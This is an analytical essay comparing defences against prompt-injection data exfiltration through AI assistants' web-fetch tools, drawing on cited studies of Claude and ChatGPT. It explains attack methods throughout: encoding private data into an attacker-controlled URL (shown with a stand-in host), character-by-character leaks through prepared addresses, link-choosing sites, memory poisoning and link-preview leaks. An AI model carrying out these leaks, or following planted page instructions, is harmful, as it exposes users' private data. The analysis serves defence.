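*An Empirical Study of Privacy Leakage Chains via Prompt Injection* (Yang, Na and Choi, 2026) includes a server log of a request that OpenAI's public-index check should have stopped. The log is from 3 February 2026, six days after OpenAI described the check. A user had asked ChatGPT to summarise a page that contained hidden instructions. Within five seconds ChatGPT requested three pages, and the last URL had a made-up birthday in its parameters.

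Perhaps OpenAI was still rolling the check out, or perhaps it didn't cover this route. The security researcher Johann Rehberger thought such gaps in coverage were likely in general. *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on his blog Embrace The Red, warns that some of OpenAI's own developers may not know about the check or apply it. One log isn't enough to tell how often such gaps occur.

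### How much fits into one request

Suppose a tool let Claude write any URL of up to 250 characters, and an attacker's address began like this:

`https://rates.example/log?q=`

That takes up 28 characters and leaves 222 for stolen data. A URL can contain 66 different characters without special encoding: 52 upper- and lower-case letters, ten digits and four punctuation marks. The capacity in bits, where one bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question, is:

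222 × log₂ 66 ≈ 1,340 bits

This is enough for about 37 English words or several passwords. If the assistant can only choose among 36 fixed addresses, one for each letter and digit, a request carries far less:

log₂ 36 ≈ 5.2 bits

Sending the same data would take about 260 requests.

Paul's pages had 27 links each, so each request could carry 4.75 bits. dyb estimates in *The Read-Only Lie* that the whole theft took roughly 30 requests and leaked 143 bits. That is about a tenth of what one constructed URL could have held, but it was enough for a name, an employer and a city.

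The next table applies this to five things a thief might want. It assumes that the data is plain text and that an assistant that can only choose among prepared addresses leaks one character per request. The times are based on Tencent Zhuque Lab's *Why AI Agent’s Memory Becomes Attacker’s Data Goldmine* (2026), which reproduced Paul's method and extracted an API key, with one to two seconds between requests. The lab had configured its test agent to follow instructions on web pages, so the test is evidence of the method's speed but not of how often a real assistant would comply.

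| What the thief wants | Characters | Requests with constructed URLs | Requests with prepared addresses | Time with prepared addresses |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Six-digit code | 6 | 1 | 6 | 6–12 seconds |
| Name, employer and hometown | 30 | 1 | 30 | 30–60 seconds |
| API key | 40 | 1 | 40 | 40–80 seconds |
| One-page letter | 3,000 | 14 | 3,000 | 50–100 minutes |
| Large mailbox | 1,000,000 | 4,505 | 1,000,000 | 12–23 days |

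The rule multiplies the number of requests needed to steal the letter or the mailbox by more than 200. It multiplies the number needed to steal the six-digit code by only six, because a constructed URL could have held far more than six characters.

Thefts that take many steps are also more likely to fail. If the assistant got each step right 99% of the time, it would finish 30 steps in 74% of attempts and would practically never finish 3,000. *Silent Egress* found that failures rose even with few steps. When the planted text told the agent to split a secret into four pieces, the share of runs in which anything reached the attacker fell from 97–100% to 60–90%, depending on where the text was.

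An attacker can, however, use fewer requests by adding addresses, and Rehberger points out that the set could grow from 36 to thousands. With 4,096 addresses that each stand for a common word, one request carries 12 bits, and a 500-word letter takes 500 requests instead of 3,000. Doubling the bits per request means squaring the number of addresses, so adding more soon brings little benefit. The attacker can also target a single fact. One bit is enough to reveal whether a user is being treated for cancer. One request can reveal which of 36 companies an employer plans to buy, and for some victims that is worth more than the whole mailbox.

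### Leaks without an instruction to leak

All of the leaks above depended on planted text getting the assistant to do something odd. *Actions Speak Louder than Words* (Liang, Deng and colleagues, 2026) showed that ordinary browsing can be enough to leak data. An innocent-looking reference sends the agent to the attacker's site, which offers links on different subjects. The agent opens the one that suits its task, and the site then offers more specific links on that subject.

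In one example, a user wants to know why influenza can be more dangerous than COVID-19 for children. The agent clicks "biological mechanisms" rather than "clinical outcomes", then "immune response" rather than "pathogenesis". The site never receives the question, but its operator can infer much of it from those two clicks.

Liang and colleagues tested four agents with three recent models on 500 questions. The site needed about 6.5 rounds per question. When it got a usable trail, it recovered the question's main concepts with an average F1 score of 0.89, where 1 means it found every concept and added no wrong ones. It scored 0.80 on profiles of users built up over several conversations. When the researchers replaced one agent's choices with random ones, the site's score fell from 0.81 to 0.10, so its accuracy came from the agent's choices and not just from good guessing.

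These agents could follow links freely. Claude on the API may do so too, and its rule would permit every step of the attack. The chat app's reported rule would stop the agent at the first link. OpenAI's index check should stop most of the attack, because the site builds its pages during the visit, before any crawler could record them. An attacker could publish fixed pages in advance, but these couldn't adapt to each visitor.

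Liang and colleagues propose that the software download everything a page links to, regardless of what the user asked, and let the agent choose among the local copies. The attacker then can't tell which page the agent wanted. This cut both scores to 0.39 but needed more than four times as many page fetches.

### Request limits and caching

A limit on the number of requests does little by itself. Under the cap of ten fetches in Anthropic's sample configuration, an assistant that could write its own URLs could still send 2,220 characters. If the assistant also can't construct URLs, the same cap lets it send about 52 bits, or ten letters and digits, which is enough for a surname but not for a 40-character API key.

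The attacker may also be able to wait for the next conversation. Radware got ChatGPT to store malicious rules in its memory, and ChatGPT then leaked data before answering each new message. A cap that resets every turn only slows down this kind of theft.

Caching also reduces the leak. If the assistant reads a stored copy when it returns to an address, the attacker's server doesn't see the second visit, so the name "Anna" arrives as "an". Rehberger suggests either keeping these copies for a few minutes or refusing repeat visits within a session. If each of 36 addresses works only once, there are about 10⁴² possible sequences of visits, which limits the leak to roughly 140 bits per session, however many requests the assistant makes.

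Both attacks that used prepared addresses avoided this problem. ZombieAgent had a separate address for each character in each position, so ten positions need 360 addresses to cover letters and digits. On Paul's site, each address contained all the letters chosen so far, so every address was new.

A public-index check is much better at stopping Paul's version. A site with a page for every ten-character string of 27 symbols would need more than 200 trillion pages, which no crawler will record. But the attacker can use a fixed set of pages instead, and 360 are easy to publish. Rehberger notes that a large blog probably has 36 suitable pages in the index already, though he hadn't tested recently whether OpenAI limits repeat visits.

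In Claude chat, an attacker who got enough pages into a search engine could in principle still steal data through Claude's choice of which search results to fetch. Each letter might need a search as well as a fetch, and the attacker would depend on the search engine to return the right pages. None of the leaks described here worked this way.

### Why the check is outside the model

Willison judges Anthropic's rule by whether an attacker can persuade the assistant to break it. Claude chat has what Willison calls the lethal trifecta: it holds private data, reads text from strangers, and can send requests to the outside. Even after the discovery of Paul's loophole, Willison wrote that the rules "deterministically block" an instruction to put private data into an address, meaning they stop it every time.

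Two studies compared defences of this kind with attempts to make the model more careful. *Silent Egress* tested each defence 30 times on a small model running on the researchers' own computer. *The Framing Gap* (Rahman and Kim, 2026) mostly attacked GPT-4o, an older OpenAI model, with instructions that presented the theft as a routine technical step.

| Defence | Study | Attacks that still succeeded |
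|---|---|---|
| None | *Silent Egress* | 100% |
| Telling the model to ignore instructions in web pages | *Silent Egress* | 67% |
| Marking web text as untrusted | *Silent Egress* | 100% |
| Both of these | *Silent Egress* | 57% |
| Domain allowlist | *Silent Egress* | 0% |
| Training a model to resist injections | Rahman and Kim | 32.5% |
| Giving the model web text in a separate channel | Rahman and Kim | 38.8% |
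| Telling the model never to reveal the secret "in any form" | Rahman and Kim | 0% |
| The same, but with a list of forbidden actions instead of "in any form" | Rahman and Kim | 48.8% |
| Allowlist of destinations | Rahman and Kim | 0% |
| Keeping the secret from the component that reads web pages | Rahman and Kim | 0% |

The percentages aren't comparable between the studies, and the allowlists scored 0% partly because the tests left the attacker's site off them. *Silent Egress* cautions that attackers can route data through a trusted site that redirects visitors elsewhere. Neither study tested a provenance-only rule. Such a rule would also have refused a URL containing the secret because, like an allowlist, it doesn't depend on the model recognising an attack.

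A provenance check also doesn't need to recognise the secret. Rahman and Kim tried a filter that looked for the secret in outgoing text, and it failed every time the model disguised the secret with a simple letter-substitution code that the filter didn't know. A provenance check would still refuse an address containing the disguised secret, because the model wrote the address.

Moving the check outside the model isn't enough. In *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026) built a monitor that records what influenced each action and can block a request that depends on both untrusted text and private data. On a standard set of attacks, it was about as secure as earlier methods that track private data, and it let the agent complete substantially more tasks. But when Liang and colleagues tested one of those earlier methods and three other defences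 against their link-choosing site, none lowered the site's scores by more than 0.03. These defences didn't treat the choice of a harmless address as a possible message, which an outside check has to do.

One could also argue that newer models make the rule unnecessary. In Liang and colleagues' study, a direct instruction to send out private data succeeded in only 0.38% of attempts. Rahman and Kim extracted no data from ChatGPT in 48 trials, although GPT-4o, when accessed through OpenAI's API, leaked data in every trial that used the most effective wordings.

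But these figures apply to particular wordings. Rahman and Kim's openly worded attacks never worked on GPT-4o, yet an attacker who tried three versions of one disguised attack would have succeeded about 96% of the time. Yang and colleagues found a similar gap in a newer ChatGPT model, where an older injection technique worked in 4 of 136 attempts and their own worked in 121 of 168. A low success rate for a known attack is therefore weak evidence that a new one will fail, and a fixed rule is most useful against wordings nobody has tried yet.

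Rehberger reported this kind of leak to OpenAI in early 2023. That December, OpenAI added its first `url_safe` check, which later blocked the flashcard links. Rehberger calls the public-index version "a significant improvement" that makes attacks more complex, but doesn't consider the problem solved.

### What the rule leaves open

The rule covers one tool, and many assistants have several. Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* describes a leak through Claude's code-running tool after Anthropic gave it network access. Claude sent the user's data out through Anthropic's file service, which the tool was allowed to contact. SecurityBuzz's *Researchers Say Claude Flaws Could Be Chained to Silently Exfiltrate User Data* reports that the security company Oasis used the same file service in an attack that began with a link to Claude and a prepared prompt.

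dyb lists six leaks in Anthropic's products between October 2025 and July 2026, and only Paul's went through the chat app's fetch tool. dyb concludes that fixes close one channel at a time while every new tool adds more. Six cases can't establish how fast the number of channels grows, but they do suggest that attackers have alternatives when the fetch tool is well protected.

Messaging apps can leak data without any tool call. PromptArmor's *Threat Intelligence* explains that apps such as Slack and Telegram load previews of links in messages. If a hijacked agent writes a link that contains private data, the app requests that link before anyone clicks it. A rule that limits what the agent may fetch doesn't prevent this, because the app makes the request. Without previews, the data would leak only if the user clicked the link, much as in paste-back.

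An assistant can also send information through the timing or number of its requests to a permitted address. Liang and colleagues tested this with four possible messages, so guessing would be right 25% of the time. When the agent responded, the number of requests revealed the right message 73.5% of the time, and their timing did so 58.6% of the time. These signals are slow and unreliable, and caching would hide most repeat visits.

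The rule doesn't prevent injection. Text on a hotel's page can still lead Claude to recommend that hotel or quote a false price, because this requires no outgoing request beyond the one the user wanted. OpenAI presents its check as one of several defenses, along with monitoring and training against injection.

False information can do more damage if the assistant stores it. Radware's researcher altered a medical history in ChatGPT's memory, which led to harmful medical advice. In Embrace The Red's *Breaking Opus 4.7 with ChatGPT (Hacking Claude's Memory)*, planted text got Claude Opus 4.7 to save false memories about the user in five of ten runs. In all ten runs, the model had either detected a possible injection or questioned whether it should store the information.

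## Which looser rules would give back the lost tasks, and at what risk?

The provenance-only rule blocks both the URL for page two of a library list and a URL that contains Mara Lind's email. A looser rule is only worth having if it allows the first and still blocks the second.

Five of the lost tasks make a fair test:

- an API query, such as the number of earthquakes in six weeks of 2019
- a site search, such as books about bridges in a library's catalogue
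- pagination, such as pages 2 to 12 of that list
- a parameter change, such as `sort=newest` in place of `sort=oldest`
- a documentation guess, such as `/v5/install` when the assistant knows only `/v4/install`

Each looser rule can be judged by which of these tasks it would restore and how much data a hijacked assistant could still send to an attacker. Changing the URL rule would not lift the fetch tool's other limits, so the assistant still could not submit POST forms or open pages behind a login.

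### The public-index check

OpenAI's check, which ChatGPT uses, restores a task only if the crawler has already recorded the exact address. It works best for guessed documentation addresses, because a manual has a modest number of public pages that link to one another, so the right address has a good chance of being in the index. Most wrong guesses won't be there, and ChatGPT can drop them without sending a request. But it can't distinguish a page that doesn't exist from one the crawler missed.

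Long lists do worse, because the assistant needs every page. Suppose the crawler had recorded each of the library's eleven later pages with a probability of 90%, independently of the others. The chance of getting the whole list would be:

0.9¹¹ ≈ 31%

Real coverage is probably more uneven, since a crawler tends to take either most of a list or only the first few pages. OpenAI gives no coverage figure. API queries and detailed site searches almost never pass, because there are far too many possible addresses to crawl.

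Rehberger writes on Embrace The Red that, as he understands it, ChatGPT treats an address the user types as safe for the rest of the chat. That would explain why it opened the brand-new pages in Chen and colleagues' prompts.

An attacker can still use already-indexed addresses as a code, at roughly 5 to 12 bits per request. OpenAI could close that channel by giving the assistant the stored copy of an indexed page instead of the live one, since the attacker's server would then receive nothing. However, the stored copy may be out of date.

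### Asking the user to confirm

A confirmation prompt could restore all five tasks if someone is there to answer it. ChatGPT already sometimes shows one when an address isn't in its index.

In its case against strict lists of trusted sites, OpenAI worries that frequent warnings train people to click through. People visit far more than a handful of well-known sites, so a strict list produces many false alarms. The same argument counts against OpenAI's own check when someone works with databases or long lists. Reading the rest of the library's list could trigger eleven warnings, all false alarms.

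Better prompts would help. The software could ask once whether the assistant may open pages 2 to 12 of a list on `library.example`, and then build the eleven addresses itself. The user would only have to check one host, and would not have to look for a strange string in each address. Showing the data instead of the URL would also help, because a user is much more likely to notice "your email address" than the same address encoded in Base64. According to OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), ChatGPT may show the user the information it would transmit.

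### Looking for information from the conversation

That feature belongs to Safe Url, which also covers navigation in OpenAI's Atlas browser, and both searches and navigation in its Deep Research tool.

OpenAI's Safe Url and its public-index check are probably the same mechanism. OpenAI says Safe Url detects information learned in the conversation, which sounds like a filter that compares each URL with the chat, but it refers readers to its account of the public-index check for details.

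A filter that actually compared URLs with the chat would allow `page=2` and `sort=newest`, which contain nothing private, and most guessed documentation URLs. It would block the earthquake query because the dates and magnitude come from the user's message, even though the user obviously wants USGS to have them. It would block a subject search at the library for the same reason.

The filter would also miss disguised data, as Rahman and Kim found when a simple letter code defeated theirs. *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (2026) explains that this is hard to fix because models transform data in ways that labels can't follow. The monitor it proposes looks for known private values and also keeps a running total of how much information the agent could have sent, so even data in an unknown code counts towards a cap.

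For a fetch tool, such a cap might be 100 bits per conversation. That would allow 27 choices of a page number from 1 to 12, or three earthquake queries at 26 bits each, but not a single address with 222 freely chosen characters, which can hold about 1,340 bits.

### Domain allowlists

An allowlist that permits constructed URLs restores all five tasks, but only on the listed sites. Codex and the version of Claude Desktop for other providers both use such lists. In Codex, developers who turn on internet access can set the permitted domains and HTTP methods.

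Redirects are one weak point, because a request can start on a permitted site and end on the attacker's unless the tool checks every redirect, as Claude Desktop does. *Silent Egress* recommends analysing the whole redirect chain.

The other weak point is a permitted site where anyone can open an account. The risk depends on what the assistant can send. An attacker with a library card can't read the library's server logs, so a GET request to the library with Mara's email in it would normally be useless to them. An agent that can upload files is much more exposed, because it may upload them to the attacker's account. After finding a leak of this kind, Rehberger suggested on Embrace The Red that Anthropic restrict Claude's code environment to the logged-in user's account. Limiting an agent to GET would also prevent most uploads. Even then, the list of permitted sites should leave out link shorteners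 and hosting services, which often show their customers who requested what.

Allowlists also treat everything on a site alike. *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues, 2026) tested a host allowlist on attacks from a standard benchmark. The allowlist blocked all five attacks that contacted another site, but the other 14 all succeeded by doing something unauthorised on the permitted site, such as adding an access key to a software project when the user had only asked for a comment. When the researchers added URL templates for the site, the system blocked all 19.

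### URL templates

A URL template fixes most of an address and leaves slots for the rest. For the library's list it could be:

`https://library.example/search?subject=bridges&page={1 to 12}`

The assistant supplies only the number, and the software rejects anything that isn't a whole number from 1 to 12. Mara's email doesn't fit. The most that one request can carry is:

log₂ 12 ≈ 3.6 bits

*Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (2026) derives almost the same limit for any output restricted to a fixed set of values. Its formula adds one to the size of the set, presumably to count a rejected value, so a set of 12 values gives log₂ 13 ≈ 3.7 bits.

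At 3.6 bits per request, an attacker would need 40 requests to obtain the 143 bits that Paul's site extracted from Claude. With only twelve pages on the list, the assistant would have to request some of them again, and the software can prevent repeat requests by storing each page after the first visit. There are about 1.3 billion ways to open some or all of twelve pages once each, in any order, so the assistant's choices could then reveal about 30 bits in total, or roughly six letters. If the software also fetches the pages in order and lets the assistant choose only where to stop, the total falls to 3.6 bits. In this example, those bits all go to the library, not the attacker.

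If the attacker runs the site, changing a page number leaks less data than following a link did on Paul's site, where each link carried 4.75 bits. The Claude API already lets Claude follow links, so letting it change small page numbers there would add little risk. In Claude chat, the same change would bring back a much smaller version of the leak that Anthropic closed in July.

Other tasks need wider slots. A menu with three sort orders carries 1.6 bits, a choice among ten versions of a manual carries 3.3, and an earthquake query with two dates and a magnitude carries 26. A search box that accepts 50 free characters can hold about 300 bits, so a template with one offers little protection unless the site itself is trustworthy. Templates also can't restore the ability to guess a documentation URL if the assistant has to invent the path and not just the version number.

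Someone also has to write the templates. *ceLLMate* (Meng, Feng and colleagues, 2025) proposes that websites publish an "agent sitemap" of the requests they accept and what each one does. A browser extension blocks any request that the policy for the user's task doesn't permit. The extension slowed browsing by 7–15% in the paper's tests.

But sites rarely publish such a file. Zingrillo and colleagues note that owners may not want to, for instance because they earn money from advertisements that people see. They also built a program that drafts templates by crawling a site. Without human corrections, its drafts covered every operation needed for 18 of 25 tasks on various websites and 18 of 26 on a copy of Reddit. The researchers want the site's owner to review each draft and the user to approve the result, which is a lot of work when the user only wants to open page two.

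For pagination, a fetch tool might instead accept an address that differs from a permitted one only in the number after `page=`, up to some modest limit. The tool would need a short list of common names for that parameter, and the rule would fail on sites that use cursors instead of page numbers, but no site would have to cooperate. Designs based on templates exist only in research so far.

### Tracking what shaped the request

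Unlike a template, which limits what a URL can contain, information-flow control tracks what data influenced the URL. The software labels each piece of data by who may read it and whether it comes from a trusted source, then carries those labels through every step. In principle, it can allow any URL that private data didn't influence.

CaMeL, a research design from Google DeepMind, does this by writing the plan before the assistant reads anything from outside. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains the method. Applied to the earthquake question, it would work like this:

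1. A planning model reads only the user's request. It writes a short program that builds the USGS address, fetches it and extracts the number.
2. An interpreter runs the program and records where each value came from.
3. A second model, which has no tools, reads the page that USGS returns and reports the number.
4. Before each request, the interpreter checks the labels against a security policy.

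The address depends only on what the user typed, so the policy can allow it. Planted text on the page could falsify the number but couldn't add a request to the program. The program can also loop through twelve pages or attach a cursor to an address, which could restore pagination even on sites that supply no links.

CaMeL is weaker when the assistant has to read something before it can plan. If the developers have reorganised the version 5 manual, the right next step depends on the contents page, which the planning model never sees. *Kairos* (2026) left CaMeL out of a test with open-ended tasks because CaMeL fixes its program before the task begins. Users or administrators must also write and maintain the policies, a burden that CaMeL's creators acknowledge and that makes Willison "deeply nervous".

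*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a Microsoft research system that lets the model plan as it goes. FIDES hides untrusted results behind variable names, so the planning model can pass a web page along without reading it. If the planning model needs information from the page, it can query an isolated second model, which returns an answer of a fixed type. A yes-or-no answer gives planted text one bit of influence over the plan, which a policy might accept even if it would reject free text. Fixed answer types apply the idea of a template's slots to incoming data.

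SPIDES is the closest of these designs to the problem of constructed URLs, because it applies such labels to a browser. Zverev, Kim and colleagues (2026), in *SPIDES*, check each page the agent wants to open against what the agent has already seen. For a site where the user has no account, the rule comes to this:

| Has the agent seen private data? | Has it read untrusted text? | May it open an address it wrote? |
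|---|---|---|
| No | No | Yes |
| Yes | No | Yes |
| No | Yes | Yes |
| Yes | Yes | Only with the user's approval, unless the site is entitled to that data |

This rule is much looser than refusing every constructed URL, and it would still stop the theft of Mara's email, where the agent had both her data and the attacker's text. But an assistant that loads notes from past conversations at the start of every chat would gain little, because it would have seen private data before opening any page. After reading one page, it would need approval to open the next. Replacing the notes with a variable until the assistant needs them avoids this.

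SPIDES is stricter on sites where the user may have an account, because opening a page there could change something in the user's name. Once the agent has read untrusted text, it needs approval to visit any of these sites. SPIDES also depends on the sites to label private and user-written content on each page. A fetch tool that isn't logged in anywhere could probably do without the approval rule and the labels.

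None of these designs has a published result for the five tasks here, but their reported success on other tasks gives a rough idea of how much they reduce task completion. AgentDojo, which appears twice in the table, is a benchmark of 97 tasks in simulated office, travel, banking and messaging apps.

| Design | Test | Ordinary tasks completed | Successful attacks | Who ran it |
|---|---|---|---|---|
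| CaMeL | AgentDojo, adapted version | 30% | 0 of 629 | Developers of a rival system |
| FIDES | AgentDojo with GPT-4o | 50% | 0 | Its developers |
| SPIDES | 56 tasks on 28 artificial websites, five recent models | 67–86% | 0 | Its developers |

The CaMeL figures come from *SecureClaw* (2026), whose own system completed 61% of the same tasks. The figures may understate CaMeL's performance, since a competing team had to adapt it to their own test. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) describes the drop in tasks completed with CaMeL on AgentDojo as comparatively modest and expects it to shrink as models get better at planning.

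The FIDES figure is an average over the four kinds of app. An ordinary agent completed 84% of tasks without any checks but only 42% when the researchers applied the same policies to it, so much of the loss comes from the policies. Replacing GPT-4o with a reasoning model doubled FIDES's lead over the ordinary agent under those policies, from 8 to 16 points.

With two of the five models, SPIDES completed more tasks than an unprotected agent, partly because it hid passwords and phishing messages that would otherwise have triggered the model provider's safety filters. It needed an average of 1.84 user approvals per completed task, and the researchers assumed that the user always recognises a bad request. Real users who approve by habit would let some attacks through.

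Labels can also be wrong in a chat app. Both FIDES and SPIDES treat the user's message as public. That works for the earthquake query, but a user who describes a medical problem and asks for nearby clinics has put private facts in a message labeled public, and a hijacked assistant could send them anywhere. If the software labeled the message private instead, any query built from it would need approval once the assistant had read a web page.

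Using the task to decide which addresses to limit is no easier. *Environment Steering* (2026) sets rules for each task, but it restricts which pages the browser may visit only if the user names a URL. A user who pasted the URL for page one of a list couldn't get page two, but there would be no limit on addresses if the user asked an open question.

Tracking data also doesn't stop an assistant from leaking information through its choices. Costa and colleagues guarantee that private data won't flow directly into a request, but someone who sees the order of requests may still infer something about that data. Liang and colleagues' link-choosing site exploited this. Costa and colleagues considered a stronger guarantee but rejected it as too restrictive, because it would essentially forbid the agent from taking any publicly visible action after reading private data.

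### Keeping private data and free browsing apart

Some users might accept such a restriction. OpenAI offers something similar in Lockdown Mode, an optional setting that it introduced for organisations in February 2026 and began to extend to personal accounts in June. In this mode, ChatGPT keeps its memory and uploaded files but can read only stored copies of web pages. According to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026), no live browsing requests leave its network.

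This stops an attacker from receiving anything through browsing, including which page the assistant chose. It restores any of the five tasks only where a stored copy exists, and it switches off Deep Research and agent mode. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* warns that connected apps may still leak data and that planted text in a stored page can still distort an answer. The user can turn the setting off for a single chat.

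The assistant could instead construct URLs and browse freely if it had no access to private data. In 2025, as Willison noted at the time, Anthropic advised developers to use web fetch only in trusted environments or with data that isn't sensitive. An assistant could apply this to part of a task by passing the earthquake question to a separate session with no memory, email or files. That session could construct any URL because it would have nothing to leak except the question.

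The handover needs some care:

- The software should write the instructions for the separate session before the assistant reads anything untrusted, or show them to the user. Otherwise a hijacked assistant could slip private data into them.
- The main assistant should treat the answer as untrusted text, and its fetch tool shouldn't accept URLs from it.

Some questions need private details. To find out whether Mara's flight is late, the separate session needs her flight number, and a malicious page could obtain that number but not the rest of the email it came from. All five tasks would work, and an attacker could receive at most a sentence or two that the user could have read first. Neither OpenAI nor Anthropic seems to offer such a mode.

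### The rules compared

The table covers GET requests to public pages. "Deployed" means that at least one company uses the rule in a product.

| Rule | Status | API query | Site search | Pagination | Parameter change | Documentation guess | What an attacker could still receive |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Provenance-only, with link following | Deployed | No | No | If linked | If linked | If linked | About 5 bits per request, through the choice of links |
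| Provenance-only, without link following | Deployed, as reported | No | No | No | No | No | Little, unless search results include the attacker's pages |
| Public-index check | Deployed | Almost never | Rarely | On well-crawled sites | On well-crawled sites | Often | About 5 to 12 bits per request, through the choice of indexed pages |
| User confirms each unseen address | Deployed | Yes, if someone answers | Yes, if someone answers | Yes, but with many prompts | Yes, if someone answers | Yes, if someone answers | Anything the user approves |
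| Filter for information from the conversation | OpenAI describes Safe Url this way, but it seems to use the index | Asks or blocks | Asks or blocks | Yes | Usually | Usually | Disguised data |
| Domain allowlist that permits constructed URLs | Deployed | On listed sites | On listed sites | On listed sites | On listed sites | On listed sites | Data sent through unchecked redirects or to an account on a listed site |
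| URL templates | Research | If the fields are narrow | Menus, but not free text | Yes, except with cursors | Yes | Version numbers, but not new paths | 3.6 bits per request for a 12-page list |
| Information-flow control | Research | Yes, unless private data and untrusted text meet | Same | Same | Same | Same, but hard for CaMeL | What the assistant's choices reveal, and anything with the wrong label |
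| Stored pages only (Lockdown Mode) | Deployed, optional | No | No | If stored | If stored | If stored | Nothing through browsing, but connected apps may leak |
| Free browsing without private data | Proposal | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | The question itself |
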